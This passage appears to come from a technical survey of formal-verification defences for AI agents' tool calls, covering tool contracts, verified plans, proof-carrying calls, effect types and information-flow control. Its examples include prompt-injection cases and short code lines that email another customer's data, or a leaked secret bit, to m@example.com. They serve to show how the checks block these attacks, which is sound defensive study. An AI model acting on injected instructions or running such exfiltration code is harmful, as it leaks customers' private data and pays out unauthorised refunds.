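A program can use these declarations to replay a trace and flag unsafe calls, such as an irreversible action that the user hasn't confirmed. Kovalenko and Redchych used this method to test whether a small open model, Qwen3-4B, would learn to ask the user for confirmation first. They trained the model on office tasks, then gave it 547 shopping tasks with tools it had never seen. Its success rate rose from 74% to 83%, but its unconfirmed purchases, cancellations and refunds also rose, from 7 to 24. The model had not seen the declarations, and had apparently learned to ask before using tools with particular names.

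Another version included the declarations in the tool descriptions and varied the tools' names during training. The count was 19, which is not a statistically significant improvement on 24, and any improvement would be hard to attribute to the declarations alone because the names also changed. A larger model might use the declarations better. But how well the model uses them matters little for a guarantee, because ordinary software can read the same declaration and hold the call until the user agrees.

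### When the description is wrong

Documentation can cover every line of a tool's contract and still be wrong about any of them. *Towards Practically-Secure Tools for AI Agents* (Adam, Lu and colleagues at Brown University, 2026) describes a prototype that works out a tool's effects from its code. The paper's main example is a tool described as "Writes `content` to the file at `path`". The tool does this, but it also sends its name and the length of the content to a metrics service, which could be a leak for a company with secret source code. The researchers added the logging to an existing server themselves to imitate a real leak in the agent software OpenClaw.

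The prototype uses static analysis, which examines all paths through the code without running it. It traces data from each argument to any function that writes a file or uses the network, and produces a short list of effects. For this tool, the list includes a network write that depends on the content. If the user's policy forbids network access for sensitive code, the client blocks the call.

Static analysis by itself blocks too much, because the file's path arrives only when the agent calls the tool and the analysis has to assume that the tool might write anywhere. Adam and colleagues therefore have developers wrap each write in a small sandbox, which compares the actual path with a policy the client sends along with the call. The analysis then checks that no write escapes its sandbox and that the code can't alter the policy before it reaches the sandbox.

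They tested this on three scenarios, which were an API key that might end up in the wrong folder, the hidden logging, and a project that might go to GitHub with a secret key inside. Each scenario had a harmless version that the system should allow and a harmful version that it should block. They recorded a model's calls once and replayed them under each form of protection.

| Protection | Correct decisions out of 6 |
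|---|---|
| None | 3 |
| One sandbox around the whole server | 3 |
| Static analysis alone | 5 |
| Static analysis with a sandbox for each effect | 6 |

Only the logging scenario involves a false description, which the researchers planted. The result therefore shows that code analysis can expose a false description, but not how common false descriptions are among public tools. The researchers also supplied a suitable policy for each case by hand.

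The refund tool would be harder to analyze because the analysis stops where the program calls a database, a shell command or a web service. It could show that the tool writes to the database, but not that it adds one row for reservation r. The prototype covers tools written in Rust, and Adam and colleagues expect more false alarms in Python and JavaScript, which many tool developers use. A client would also need evidence that a remote server runs the code that was analyzed. For this, Adam and colleagues propose remote attestation, which uses secure hardware to certify which program is running on a machine.

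### Inferring contracts from documents and past calls

In *Contract2Tool*, Babu and Iyer (2026) had language models write the contracts. They made up 100 calendar, email and file tools and wrote a reference contract for each. The models had to reconstruct what each tool requires, what it produces and how risky it is. Averaged over the models, the whole contract matched the reference 43% of the time when a model saw only the tool's name, and 54% when it also saw the description and schema. The best result was 77%, from Claude Opus 4.8 with both documentation and records of the state before and after calls.

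The records helped because documentation often describes what a person would see. For example, a calendar search "returns a list of events", but the next tool needs the identifier of one event, and the change of state showed that the search had supplied it. But most of the records came from successful runs, so the inferred contract would miss an effect that appears only when a call fails, or only once in a thousand calls.

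Babu and Iyer used the contracts to choose which tool to show an agent at each step. Over 102 tasks, agents succeeded 98% of the time with inferred contracts and 99% with the reference ones, compared with 77.5% when they saw all 100 tools. Small errors do little harm in this use, because a contract only has to make the right tool appear at the right moment. They matter more in a proof, because a verifier would treat every line of a contract as true. About 23 of the 100 best contracts differed from the reference somewhere, though some of the differences were harmless. The contracts are also much simpler than the refund contract. They list conditions such as "has an event identifier", with no amounts or frame conditions, and the tools only simulated their effects. Babu and Iyer recommend that people review contracts for tools that send, delete or share things.

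Models can also write contracts closer in form to the refund example. In *Beyond Postconditions* (2025), models turn plain-language descriptions into preconditions and postconditions for Python functions, written as executable assertions. Trofimov and Novikov argue that a contract, wherever it comes from, should mark each property as established, assumed or unknown. In the refund contract, the client can establish a > 0 by checking the argument, but it has to assume the frame condition until somebody analyses the code or proves that it meets the condition.

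### Checking a contract after each call

A program can test a postcondition while the agent works. Before a refund, it reads t and paid(r). After the call, it reads them again and checks that the total is t + a and paid(r) hasn't changed. This would catch a tool that pays the wrong amount, resets paid(r) or records the refund twice. It would also catch the tool that adds its rows overnight, because the total would still be t when the call returned. The check should read the database directly if it can. If it queries the same server that issued the refund, one bug could corrupt both the refund and the values used to check it.

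The check runs too late to stop the payment, although it can stop the next one. It reads only two tables, so it misses a copy of the customer's details that the tool sends to another company. It also misses changes to other people's reservations unless it compares all the reservations before and after, which is slow for a large airline and raises false alarms whenever staff are working at the same time. It can't detect changes made after the reply either, so if a nightly job reverses the refund or issues it again, the check will already have passed.

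### When the service changes

A tool's contract can become false when the provider updates the tool. Suppose the contract for cancel_reservation has a frame condition that cancelling leaves refunds unchanged, and the provider then updates the tool so that cancelling also refunds the customer automatically. Using the same verified plan and proof as before, an agent looks up a $300 reservation with no earlier refunds, cancels it and refunds $300, so the customer receives $600 in total.

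The Model Context Protocol (MCP) only partly ensures that clients learn of such changes. It recommends that a server notify subscribed clients when its list of tools changes, but the update to the cancellation tool could leave its name, schema and description unchanged. Clients may also keep a copy of the list for as long as the server allows, which is five minutes in one of the protocol's examples. Version numbers don't reliably show a change either, because servers report their own and the protocol doesn't verify them.

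Babu and Iyer suggest updating contracts automatically from new documentation and call records, though they didn't test this on tools that change. An airline that owns its tools can do better by tying each contract to a version of the code and repeating the proof before every release. For another company's service, it can run a set of known cases against a test account every day and keep the postcondition checks on. A single mismatch is reason to suspend every plan whose proof used that contract, so the airline also needs to record which proofs depend on which contracts.

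## Proving a plan safe before it runs

Once each tool has a contract, software can reason about a series of calls without making any of them. The agent writes its whole plan first, and a verifier checks every path through it against the specification. Soteria, built by He and colleagues at Princeton University and the data company Snowflake, works this way. It translates the plan into formulas, sends them to the Dafny verifier, and reports any failure to the model, which then repairs the plan. The team's experiments show that an agent with a verified plan can still break the rules.

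### Turning a plan into formulas

In Soteria, a plan is a guarded transition system, a kind of flowchart. Each box is a state (a stage of the procedure), and each arrow is a transition that makes at most one tool call. An arrow can have a guard, a condition that must be true for the plan to take it. The plan ends in an accepting state if it has completed the task, or in a halting state if it can't safely continue.

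The table below shows a faulty plan for cancelling reservation r. The airline allows cancellation within 24 hours of booking, but only if nobody has flown yet, and the plan leaves out the second condition.

| State | What the plan does there | Next state | What the verifier knows on arrival |
|---|---|---|---|
| LOOKUP | resv = get_reservation(r) | CHECK_AGE | r is a valid reservation number |
| CHECK_AGE | hrs = hours since booking | CHECK_RULES | Also, resv holds the details of r |
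| CHECK_RULES | Makes no call | DO_CANCEL if hrs ≤ 24, otherwise NOT_PERMITTED | Also, hrs is the time since booking |
| DO_CANCEL | cancel_reservation(r) | DONE | Also, hrs ≤ 24 |

The last column is the symbolic state, written Σ(s) for state s. It is a formula that is true of every combination of values the plan's variables could have at that point, so it covers all reservations at once. The verifier works it out arrow by arrow. Suppose an arrow leaves s under guard g and calls a tool with arguments v, storing the result in x. If the tool's postcondition is Q, the arrow carries this formula to the next state:

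> Σ(s) ∧ g ∧ Q(v, x)

When several arrows lead to the same state, the verifier joins their formulas with "or", because execution could have followed any of them.

From the symbolic states, Soteria generates verification conditions, which are formulas that must always be true for the plan to be correct. They fall into three groups:

- Contracts: every call must satisfy the tool's precondition P, so Σ(s) ∧ g ⇒ P(v).
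- Progress: some run must be able to reach each state, so Σ(s) can't contradict itself. The plan must also never get stuck, so Σ(s) ⇒ g₁ ∨ … ∨ gₙ, where g₁ to gₙ are the guards on the arrows leaving s.
- Policy: every formula in the specification must hold wherever the plan can end.

The faulty plan can't get stuck at CHECK_RULES, because its guards hrs ≤ 24 and hrs > 24 cover every case. If the second guard were hrs > 25, neither guard would cover a booking made 24.5 hours ago, so Dafny would reject the plan.

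The policy conditions need more than the symbolic state, because a rule about the order of calls refers to the past. Soteria therefore adds ghost state, meaning records that exist only in the proof. These are a step counter, a log of the calls to each tool that the rules mention, and the tags that track where each value came from. Let checks and cancels be the logs for check_flown and cancel_reservation, and let |checks| be the number of entries in the first. The rule that the agent must check before it cancels becomes:

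> for every i with 0 ≤ i < |cancels|, there is a j with 0 ≤ j < |checks| such that checks[j].step < cancels[i].step, checks[j].r = cancels[i].r and checks[j].result = false

This condition holds at NOT_PERMITTED, where the plan has cancelled nothing, but fails at DONE, where cancels has one entry and checks has none. The formula then requires a j with 0 ≤ j < 0, and no such number exists. Dafny reports the error, and Soteria reports the failed rule to the planner.

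To repair the plan, the model has to add a call to check_flown and branch on the result, cancelling only when nobody has flown. The call alone isn't enough, because it might find that the passenger has flown, and the formula requires that to be false. With the branch, the guard adds the fact that nobody has flown to the symbolic state at DO_CANCEL, and the proof succeeds.

Soteria's symbolic state describes the plan's variables, not the airline's database. Its contracts relate a tool's inputs to its outputs and have no frame conditions. To enforce the refund limit, a plan could fetch the total refunded so far and compare it with the amount paid. Dafny could then prove that the comparison always comes before the refund payment, but not that the total is still correct when the refund payment runs.

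### Building plans from verified parts

Requests often combine several procedures, such as a cancellation and a refund. Soteria keeps a library of sub-plans, one for each standard procedure, and verifies each separately. A larger plan can then call a sub-plan as if it were a tool. The verifier checks the sub-plan's precondition at the point of the call and assumes its postcondition afterwards, without examining the steps in between. A rule that spans two sub-plans, such as a refund after every cancellation, must therefore be expressed in their preconditions and postconditions.

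He and colleagues tested the library on the airline tasks with GPT-5.4-mini, a small OpenAI model. Soteria writes a new plan at each turn and lets the model retry up to eight times. With sub-plans, 65 of 68 planning turns produced a verified plan, compared with 38 of 60 when the model had to write everything as one plan. The typical plan shrank from 11 states to 8, and the share that passed on the first attempt rose from 23.3% to 48.5%. The remaining failures were also easier to fix, because most were syntax errors, whereas without sub-plans the model kept violating the specification and had to redesign the plan.

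### What the evaluation found

The full evaluation used 207 tasks and four models: GPT-5.4-mini, Gemini 3 Flash, Claude Haiku 4.5 and Claude Opus 4.6. The airline and retail tasks are simulated conversations with customers. The other 43 tasks come from Toolathlon, a benchmark of long jobs involving files, documents and the command line. An agent succeeds only if it completes the task without breaking a rule. The table gives the results for Claude Opus 4.6, the strongest of the four. The alternatives to proving a plan safe are using no safeguards, having a second model judge each call, and using either of two runtime monitors from other research groups.

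| Tasks | Number | Formulas | Success with the best alternative | Success with Soteria | Cost per task without safeguards | Cost per task with Soteria |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Airline | 50 | 24 | 56.0% | 88.0% | $0.32 | $0.80 |
| Retail | 114 | 33 | 46.5% | 90.4% | $0.37 | $0.64 |
| Toolathlon | 43 | 41 | 11.6% | 18.6% | $0.97 | $0.43 |

With Soteria, no model broke a rule in any task, while the best alternative kept every rule in 93% of tasks. The plans also helped agents finish their work. In one retail task, Opus without safeguards identified the customer, the order and the product over 11 calls, then passed the customer to a human instead of making the exchange. With a plan that specified the exchange, Opus completed the task in 11 calls.

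The results are weaker in two places. On Toolathlon, Opus completed 30.2% of the tasks without safeguards, counting those where it broke rules, and 18.6% with Soteria. An owner who considers some of those rules minor might prefer the agent without safeguards. He and colleagues repeated the airline test five times with GPT-5.4-mini, allowing three retries instead of eight to save money. Soteria succeeded in 50.8% of tasks on average and AgentSpec, one of the runtime monitors, in 48.0%. That difference is within the margin of error, although Soteria again had no violations and AgentSpec averaged 4.4 per run.

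### Why agents with verified plans broke rules

To see what each part of Soteria contributes, He and colleagues added the parts one at a time on the 50 airline tasks.

| Configuration | GPT-5.4-mini: success | GPT-5.4-mini: violations | Gemini 3 Flash: success | Gemini 3 Flash: violations |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Unverified plan | 44% | 13 | 32% | 27 |
| Plan verification added | 46% | 10 | 32% | 24 |
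| Sub-plans added | 50% | 12 | 38% | 22 |
| Runtime monitor added | 60% | 0 | 62% | 0 |

Verification removed only three violations for each model. The monitor removed all the rest.

Proving a plan safe doesn't guarantee a safe run, mainly because a language model carries out the plan and by default doesn't have to follow it. Soteria shows the model a list of the remaining steps and shortens it as results arrive, but the model can call any tool it likes. A proof that every path through the plan includes the check for flown flights doesn't cover an agent that leaves the plan and cancels straight away. Some plans also lack a complete proof. When the retries run out, Soteria uses the plan that satisfies the most rules and warns the model about the remaining rules.

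Soteria also has a strict mode, which allows only the calls that the plan permits in its current state. It accepts only fully verified plans and doesn't use the monitor, so the guarantee depends on the proof. Strict mode is less flexible than the default mode. If a customer asks the agent to cancel one reservation and look up another, but the plan covers only the cancellation, strict mode blocks the harmless lookup. The default mode allows it because it breaks no rule. The evaluation used the default mode, so it didn't measure how many tasks agents could complete in strict mode.

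The perfect score is good evidence that the monitor works, but not that the formulas capture the airline's policy. He and colleagues measured conformance against the same formulas that the monitor enforces, so a working monitor should prevent every violation of a rule about permitted calls. They also corrected the formulas during their audit, so the test tasks helped to shape the specification.

The success rate is the better evidence for planning. But the experiment never combined the monitor with an agent that had no plan, so it can't separate the effect of planning from that of the monitor. He and colleagues translated their rules into AgentSpec's format for the closest comparison. AgentSpec's success rate was 50% with GPT-5.4-mini and 36% with Gemini 3 Flash, compared with 60% and 62% for the full system.

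### Asking the agent for a proof

In Soteria, Dafny's solver searches for a proof, so nobody has to write one. Meijer proposes making the agent responsible for showing that its plan is safe. The model writes the plan, a list of steps, before it sees any data. If a user asks for a summary of new emails, the plan is to fetch them, summarise them and return the summary. If one of the emails tells the agent to forward everything to a stranger, it can spoil the summary but can't add a call that sends it anywhere, because the plan is already fixed.

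An attacker can still influence the plan through text that the model reads before writing it, such as a tool's description. Meijer therefore adds a check between writing the plan and running it. A policy could forbid emailing data from the inbox to anyone outside the company, and an existing program-analysis tool such as CodeQL could search the plan for data flows that break this rule. Meijer concedes that nobody has formally measured how planning first affects an agent's usefulness, and expects some checks to remain at run time.

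In a 2026 talk, Meijer described a stricter version of the idea, in which the model returns a program with a proof and a separate component runs the program only if the proof is valid. AI Engineer's *Make the Agent Produce a Program Before It Can Act* (2026), a conference write-up of the talk, includes a small example in Lean. Plans in the example can read files, delete files and return an answer. The definition of a safe plan has rules for reading files and returning an answer but none for deleting files, so no plan that deletes a file can be proved safe.

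The example plan reads a file and reports its length. The plan's next step could depend on the file's contents, so the proof has to cover every string the file might contain. The guarantee still depends on the component that runs the plan. As AI Engineer points out, the proof would not help if that component secretly deleted a file whenever it was supposed to read one.

*Return of the Theorem* (Meijer, 2026) describes a more automatic version. Business rules are written as Horn clauses, statements such as "if the booking is insured and the flight is cancelled, then a refund is due", and a solver checks the agent's plan against them. These are designs with worked examples rather than tested systems.

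*Proof-Carrying Contracts* (Ciliberto, Rudi and Tassi, 2026) requires a proof with each call instead of each plan. The agent runs inside a program called the Airlock, which holds the passwords, money and documents that the task requires. To make a call, the agent must submit a Lean proof that the call keeps an agreed condition true. The Airlock works out the statement to prove, so the agent can't substitute an easier one.

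That statement has to allow for what the agent can't see. Let v be the agent's view of the current state. Let D(i, s, s′) mean that a call with input i, starting in state s, could pass through or end in state s′. The agent must prove:

> for every state s that satisfies C and has view v: some s′ satisfies D(i, s, s′), and every s′ with D(i, s, s′) satisfies C

Without the first part, the Airlock would allow a call on any input for which D describes no outcome, because the second part would be true with no cases to check. D must also include changes that other people make during the call. If the airline's staff can refund the same reservation at any moment, an agent can't prove that refunding the customer's last $100 is safe. Writing a proof takes time, so the proof must stay valid for a set number of the Airlock's control steps before the call starts.

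The main example is a travel agency's agent that books a trip for a family. The contract limits spending to 2,000 euros and allows only hotels with a recorded rating of at least 7. The agent tries to book a partner hotel that pays the agency commission, but the Airlock rejects the call because the hotel has no rating. The agent then requests a rating, which comes back as 5, so there is no valid proof that the booking meets the contract. Later, the agent receives an email with instructions to send the passport to an unapproved address, and the Airlock rejects that call as well. The Airlock can reject both calls without recognising the conflict of interest or the attack.

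Ciliberto and colleagues prove that C holds from the start of a contract until it closes, whatever the agent requests. The theorem assumes a sound proof checker, tool models that cover everything the tools can do, and an Airlock that runs as designed. It also assumes that the Airlock's control routine activates the contract only when C holds, and keeps C true whenever it runs between the agent's calls. They haven't yet measured how often agents can find the proofs, how long that takes, or how much useful work the agents get done.

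Proving one call at a time can also leave the agent unable to finish a task, because each proof covers only the next call. The family needs hotels for three nights. The agent could spend 900 euros on the first night and 1,000 on the second, with a valid proof each time, and stay within the budget but have too little left for the third. If the prices were known in advance, verifying a plan that booked all three nights within the budget would avoid this.

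### Proving something simpler than a plan

Other systems verify something that changes less often than an agent's plans. In *VeriGuard*, a Google system (Miculicich, Parmar and colleagues, 2025), a model turns a safety request into a Python function that decides whether to allow an action, and writes the function's precondition and postcondition. Nagini, an automated verifier for Python, then proves that the function satisfies them. The agent's plan needs no proof, because the function checks each action as it comes up.

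The weak point is the function's input. At run time, another language model reads the agent's text and extracts the function's arguments. Suppose a proved function allows only refunds within the limit. If the model reads $150 as $50, the function correctly approves a refund of $50, and the agent pays out $150. A model can also write the wrong conditions, so Miculicich and colleagues ask the user to review them.

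On a benchmark of attacks against agents, VeriGuard reduced the attackers' success rate to zero with all four models tested. A simpler defence, in which a model directly judged whether each action followed the policy, did the same, but agents completed more of their real tasks with VeriGuard (for example, 85.1% against 68.3% with Claude Sonnet 4). The benchmark showed little benefit from the proof step. When Miculicich and colleagues added VeriGuard's parts one by one, successful attacks fell to zero before they added formal verification.

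*Agentproof* (Xavier, Jolly and colleagues, 2026) checks workflows that developers write in advance. Popular frameworks such as LangGraph and CrewAI let a developer define an agent's work as a graph of model calls, tool calls and human approvals. Agentproof extracts the graph and searches it. To test whether a person must approve every refund, it removes all the approval steps and looks for a path that still reaches the refund tool. If it finds one, it shows it to the developer.

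Agentproof converts each rule about order into a finite automaton and searches the graph and the automaton together. The number of combinations is at most the number of graph nodes times the number of automaton states, so the search always finishes, even when the graph contains loops. The basic graph checks took about 105 milliseconds on a graph of 5,000 nodes.

The search is fast because it ignores data. It treats every branch as possible, so it can raise a false alarm about a path that no real run would take. It also can't tell whether a check and a cancellation concern the same reservation. The rule language can't refer to the past, so a rule can't directly require a check before each cancellation. Its version of "a refund follows every cancellation" is violated only if a second cancellation comes before the refund, so a workflow that cancels once and then stops without issuing a refund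 would pass.

Xavier and colleagues tested Agentproof on 18 small workflows they had written themselves. It found the structural faults they had planted in five of them, but this doesn't show how common such faults are in real systems. The result also depends on extracting each workflow's graph correctly. In LangGraph, Agentproof identifies human approval steps by the word "human" in their names, so a step called notify_human could count as an approval even if it only sent a message.

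The table compares what each approach proves and what it takes for granted.

| Work | What the proof or check covers | Who produces it | Who checks it | Main assumptions |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| He and colleagues | Every path through one plan | Dafny's solver | Dafny | The contracts are true and the agent follows the plan |
| Meijer, 2026 talk | Every run of one plan | The agent's model | A proof checker such as Lean | The component that runs the plan does what each step means |
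| Ciliberto and colleagues | One tool call | The agent or a separate prover | Lean, inside the Airlock | The tool models cover all real effects and nothing bypasses the Airlock |
| Miculicich and colleagues | The function that judges each action | Nagini's solver | Nagini | The conditions are right and a model extracts the right arguments |
| Xavier and colleagues | Every path through a fixed workflow | A graph search | The same search | The extracted graph is accurate and doesn't change during a run |

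### Plans with loops

Soteria rejects any plan whose arrows form a cycle, because its verifier has to process each state after all the states that lead to it. A plan can apply one action to every item in a list, but it can't keep searching for flights until one has a free seat. To retry, the planner can write out a fixed number of attempts, which makes the plan longer, or end the plan and write a new one.

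Program verifiers usually handle loops with a loop invariant, a statement that is true before the loop starts and that each pass keeps true. If an agent refunds a list of reservations one after another, the invariant could be that no reservation has received more than the customer paid. The verifier checks that a single pass keeps this true, which requires the code to compare each refund with that limit before paying it. The proof then covers a list of any length. Somebody has to find the invariant, though a language model can suggest one and the verifier will reject it if it is wrong.

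The Lean format in AI Engineer's example allows some loops without a special construct. A plan could read a file that lists other files and then read each of those, and a proof by induction on the list would cover lists of any length. But every run of such a plan must end after finitely many steps, so the format can't express an agent that watches an inbox indefinitely.

### Decisions that depend on free text

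Many plans have to branch on something a person wrote. The airline lets an insured customer cancel for reasons of health or weather. If the customer writes "my mother's operation has moved to Friday", the agent has to decide whether that counts as a health reason, which no guard can test directly.

In Soteria, a plan can hand such a decision to a language model and state a condition that the answer must satisfy. The verifier assumes that the answer satisfies the condition. At run time, Soteria checks the answer, asks the model again if the check fails, and halts after a set number of failures. This works well when ordinary software can check the condition. In one of He and colleagues' examples, a model selects suitable flights, and the condition is that each flight has enough seats for all the passengers.

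When the model classifies the customer's message, software can check only that the answer is "health", "weather" or "other". The proof shows that the plan handles each answer correctly, but not that the model chose the right one. The specification may not catch a wrong choice either. One of He and colleagues' example plans tests the customer's reason, but their printed cancellation rule accepts any insured booking, so an agent that misread the message would still count as conforming.

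Ciliberto and colleagues handle such judgements by having both parties agree on an expert, such as a particular model with a fixed prompt. The contract treats the expert's answer as true, and the Airlock records it so that the agent can't keep asking until it gets a better one. This settles disputes between the parties, but a hotel could still write its description to impress the expert, and proofs that use the resulting rating would remain valid.

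### When the plan has to change

Conversations rarely go as planned, so Soteria writes and verifies a new plan each time the customer replies. With Claude Opus 4.6, planning took a median of 2.7 seconds per turn, and under eight seconds on 99% of turns. Repeated planning is the main reason Soteria costs more than the alternatives on airline and retail tasks. It costs less than they do on Toolathlon, because each task there needs only one plan.

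Replanning weakens the protection that Meijer gets from planning before reading any data. If the agent reads an attacker's email and then plans again, the email can influence the second plan. The verifier still checks that plan, but it only stops attacks that the specification rules out. Telling an agent to replan after a violation isn't enough to stop attacks either. When VeriGuard reported each violation to the agent and prompted it to replan, but didn't block any tool calls, 11.9% of attacks succeeded on average. Also blocking the offending call brought this close to zero.

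Soteria's strict mode lets the model retry a call after a network error. If a refund succeeds but the reply is lost, the model may issue it again, even though the verified plan contains it only once.

Even if every plan passes verification and the agent follows each one exactly, the whole conversation can break a rule. One of He and colleagues' airline rules requires an agent that has looked up a reservation to run the flown check before transferring the customer to a human. Suppose the first plan looks up the reservation and ends by asking the customer a question. The reply leads to a second plan, which transfers the customer immediately. The first plan contains no transfer and the second contains no lookup, so each satisfies the rule alone, but together they violate it. Soteria's Dafny encoding starts every plan with empty logs, so it would accept both. Soteria's runtime monitor would block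 the transfer because it keeps the trace of all earlier calls. The verifier could also catch the problem if it started the second plan's logs with the calls the agent had already made.

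## Limiting effects with types, capabilities and information flow

Soteria needs a new proof for every plan, and a long conversation can require many plans. A restricted programming language avoids this because one proof about the language covers every program written in it. The compiler's type checker then automatically examines each program and rejects any that combine values in forbidden ways.

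An airline could use this to rule out emails that contain another customer's data and refunds whose amounts came from text the customer wrote. Either can result from prompt injection, an attack that hides instructions in text the agent was only meant to read.

### Effects in a program's type

In most languages, a function whose type promises a whole number may also delete a file before returning it. An effect type lists what a program may do as well as what it returns. Let Γ ⊢ e : A ! ε mean that, given the variables in Γ, program e returns a value of type A and can cause no effect outside the set ε. The rule for doing one thing after another is:

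> if Γ ⊢ e₁ : A ! ε₁ and Γ, x : A ⊢ e₂ : B ! ε₂, then Γ ⊢ (let x = e₁ in e₂) : B ! ε₁ ∪ ε₂

The program runs e₁, names the result x, and then runs e₂, which may use x. The whole program can cause any effect that either part can. If get_reservation has the set {read} and refund has {pay}, a program that uses both has {read, pay}. In a simple system like this one, no rule removes an effect from the set, so if a helper function makes a refund, pay still appears in the type of the whole program. An airline that wants an agent only to answer questions can accept only programs of type Text ! {read}, and the checker will reject any program that might pay.

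Haskell has long worked in roughly this way, using the type `IO` to mark code that interacts with the outside world. Zhou, D'Antoni and Polikarpova (2026), in *Language-Based Agent Control*, apply this approach to agents with a library called ELBA. A developer calls the function `agent` with a prompt, a list of permitted functions and the type that the result must have. The model writes a Haskell program, and the compiler checks it against that type. The program runs if it passes the check; otherwise, the model gets the error message and tries again.

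When the required type is a plain integer, the program can calculate but can't cause any effect, so a program that deletes the server's files and then returns a factorial won't compile. For tasks that need effects, the developer defines an effect type narrower than IO. In the main example, a type called BibIO lets a program search a database of publications, fetch an entry, and append an entry to a bibliography. Haskell's general function for writing files has type IO, so a BibIO program can't use it. The generated program may call `agent` again, for instance after reading search results, but the new program must also fit the type at that point. A parent agent can give a sub-agent fewer effects than it has, but never more.

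Zhou and colleagues prove that any property the type system guarantees for ordinary programs also holds for programs that call agents. The proof replaces each agent call with an ordinary function that requests a program, type-checks it and runs it. The result is an ordinary program in the same language, so the existing guarantee applies. Induction extends the proof to agents that call other agents. The theorem holds whatever code the model returns, provided that the language's own guarantee is sound, all generated code is checked before it runs, and the developer's surrounding code is in the same language. Haskell also has loopholes that let a program disguise an effect as a pure value, so generated code must stay within Safe Haskell, a subset without them. The proof was done by hand rather than in a proof assistant.

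A typed language limits effects only if its types record them. Liu (2026), in *λ_A*, defines a typed calculus for composing agents and proves 42 theorems about it in the proof assistant Coq, now called Rocq. For example, a loop with a step limit always stops if its model and tool calls do. But tools have ordinary function types, so a tool that pays a refund can have the same type as one that looks up a booking. Liu leaves an effect system to later work.

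### Permission as a value

An effect type can allow or forbid refunds in general, but the airline wants to allow them only for the customer in the conversation. It can do this with a capability, which is an unforgeable reference that a program must hold to cause a given effect. In one of Zhou and colleagues' examples, a program can open a file only with a value of type Path, and it can't make a Path from a string of text. The program is given a Path for a folder and can narrow it to files inside that folder. Similarly, the airline could give each program an object called desk whose refund method works only on one customer's reservations. Even if the program knew another customer's reservation number, it couldn't refund that reservation, because it has no object that can.

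Programs can store capabilities and pass them around, so a harmless-looking function might contain one that sends email. *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (Odersky, Zhao and colleagues, 2026) addresses this with capture checking, an experimental feature of the language Scala 3. Each type records which capabilities its values can reach. A function of type `String -> Int` can reach none, so it is pure, meaning it has no side effects. A function of type `String ->{mail} Int` can use the capability `mail`. The paper's system, TACIT, is an MCP server that accepts Scala code from any compatible agent.

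Capture checking can also limit how long a program keeps a capability. In TACIT, a program can use files only inside a block of code that requests access to a folder. In one benchmark run, an agent wrote a program that tried to return a list of file handles from such a block, and the compiler rejected the program because the handles still contained the permission.

Some Scala features, such as unchecked type conversions and reflection, would let capabilities go untracked, so TACIT compiles everything in a safe mode that forbids those features. Machine-checked proofs cover the core type system behind capture checking. Odersky and colleagues acknowledge that they need a further argument to show that safe mode provides the intended guarantees. They also trust the compiler, the runtime and TACIT's library of about 1,000 lines. If the agent may run an external command, the types can't limit what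 that command does.

### When a customer's note contains instructions

Suppose a customer who paid $300 writes in the note on the reservation that a manager has approved a $900 refund. The customer also writes that the agent should email the passenger details of reservation q to m@example.com. The model acts on the note by writing code to issue the refund and send the email.

To protect the refund, the airline can follow the pattern that Zhou and colleagues use for bibliographies. The airline's library gives the amount paid the type Trusted Money, and the refund tool accepts only that type. Ordinary code can't create a Trusted value. The note is plain text, and amount_in extracts a plain Money value from it, which the refund tool doesn't accept.

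```
resv = get_reservation(r)
refund(r, amount_in(resv.note))
```

The checker rejects the second line because refund requires Trusted Money and amount_in returns Money. If the model read the note itself and wrote refund(r, 900), the checker would reject that too, since a number typed into the program is plain Money. It would accept refund(r, resv.paid).

For the email, the airline can use Classified, a wrapper from TACIT. If other customers' records arrive inside it, a program can transform them with its map method, which accepts only pure functions and returns the result in a new wrapper.

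```
other = get_reservation(q)
other.map(o => mail.send("m@example.com", o.passengers))
```

The compiler rejects the second line. The function has type `Reservation ->{mail} Unit`, where Unit means it returns nothing useful, but map requires `Reservation -> Unit`. The compiler would report that mail cannot flow into an empty capture set. Odersky and colleagues recorded similar errors when agents tried to print a secret key or write classified text to a file. The agent can't get around this by printing the wrapper, because it sees only asterisks where the user sees the contents. It can still use the record, for example by asking a separate, trusted model for a summary, which comes back in its own wrapper.

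Both rejections happen before any tool runs, and neither requires the checker to recognise an attack. But the Trusted type doesn't stop this program:

```
if "manager" in resv.note: refund(r, resv.paid)
```

The refund amount comes from the airline's records, but whether the airline pays depends on the customer's note. Wrapping the note in Classified would prevent this, since a program can't branch on wrapped text and then pay a refund. But it would also prevent the agent from acting on anything the customer wrote.

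### Following information through decisions

Information-flow control tracks how data influences both values and decisions. For agents, much of this work starts from CaMeL, which Debenedetti, Shumailov and colleagues presented in *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* (2025). CaMeL uses two models. One writes a program in a subset of Python and never reads untrusted text. The other reads the text and returns values from it, but has no tools. A custom interpreter runs the program, labels each value with its sources, and checks a policy before sensitive calls. As in Meijer's design, the customer's note can't add a call to the program. A refund amount taken from the note is also labeled with its source, so the policy can block the refund.

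CaMeL has no soundness theorem. Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow*, found that its interpreter can leak secrets through a branch that the program doesn't take. The following version of their example reveals whether another customer paid more than $1,000:

```
tmp = True
rich = True
if other.paid > 1000: tmp = False
if tmp: rich = False
if rich: send_email("m@example.com", "yes")
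```

If the customer paid $1,200, the third line sets tmp to False and labels it secret. The program then skips the assignment on the fourth line, so rich keeps its value of True and its public label, and the email goes out. If the customer paid $300, rich becomes False and no email goes out. The interpreter never labels rich as secret, although its value depends entirely on the secret.

Garby and colleagues also found a leak in how CaMeL retries. Whether a program is blocked or allowed can reveal one bit about a secret, and CaMeL's retry loop runs outside the interpreter, where nothing tracks labels. An attacker who can keep retrying with different thresholds can find a whole-dollar amount below $1,024 in ten attempts.

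To rule out all such leaks, a proof needs a definition that doesn't depend on how an interpreter assigns labels. The usual one is noninterference, which means that changing the secret inputs never changes the public outputs:

> for all public inputs p and secret inputs s and s′: public(run(p, s)) = public(run(p, s′))

The same definition works for untrusted text, with "untrusted" in place of "secret" and "trusted" in place of "public". For the airline, this means replacing the note with any other text would leave every refund unchanged. Noninterference compares two runs, whereas Alpern and Schneider's safety and liveness properties concern one run at a time. We can't tell from a trace containing a $300 refund whether a different note would have changed it. A mechanism that watches a single run must therefore be stricter than the definition and stop some runs that would have leaked nothing.

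Garby and colleagues proved a form of noninterference for every program in LLMbda, a small language for writing agents. Each value has a label, which can include U for untrusted and S for secret, and labels combine like Soteria's tags. When a program branches on the note, everything it computes inside the branch gets U in its label. If the refund tool requires an amount without U, the program stops when it tries to refund an amount computed in that branch. LLMbda checks this while the program runs, so the agent may already have cancelled the reservation when the refund fails.

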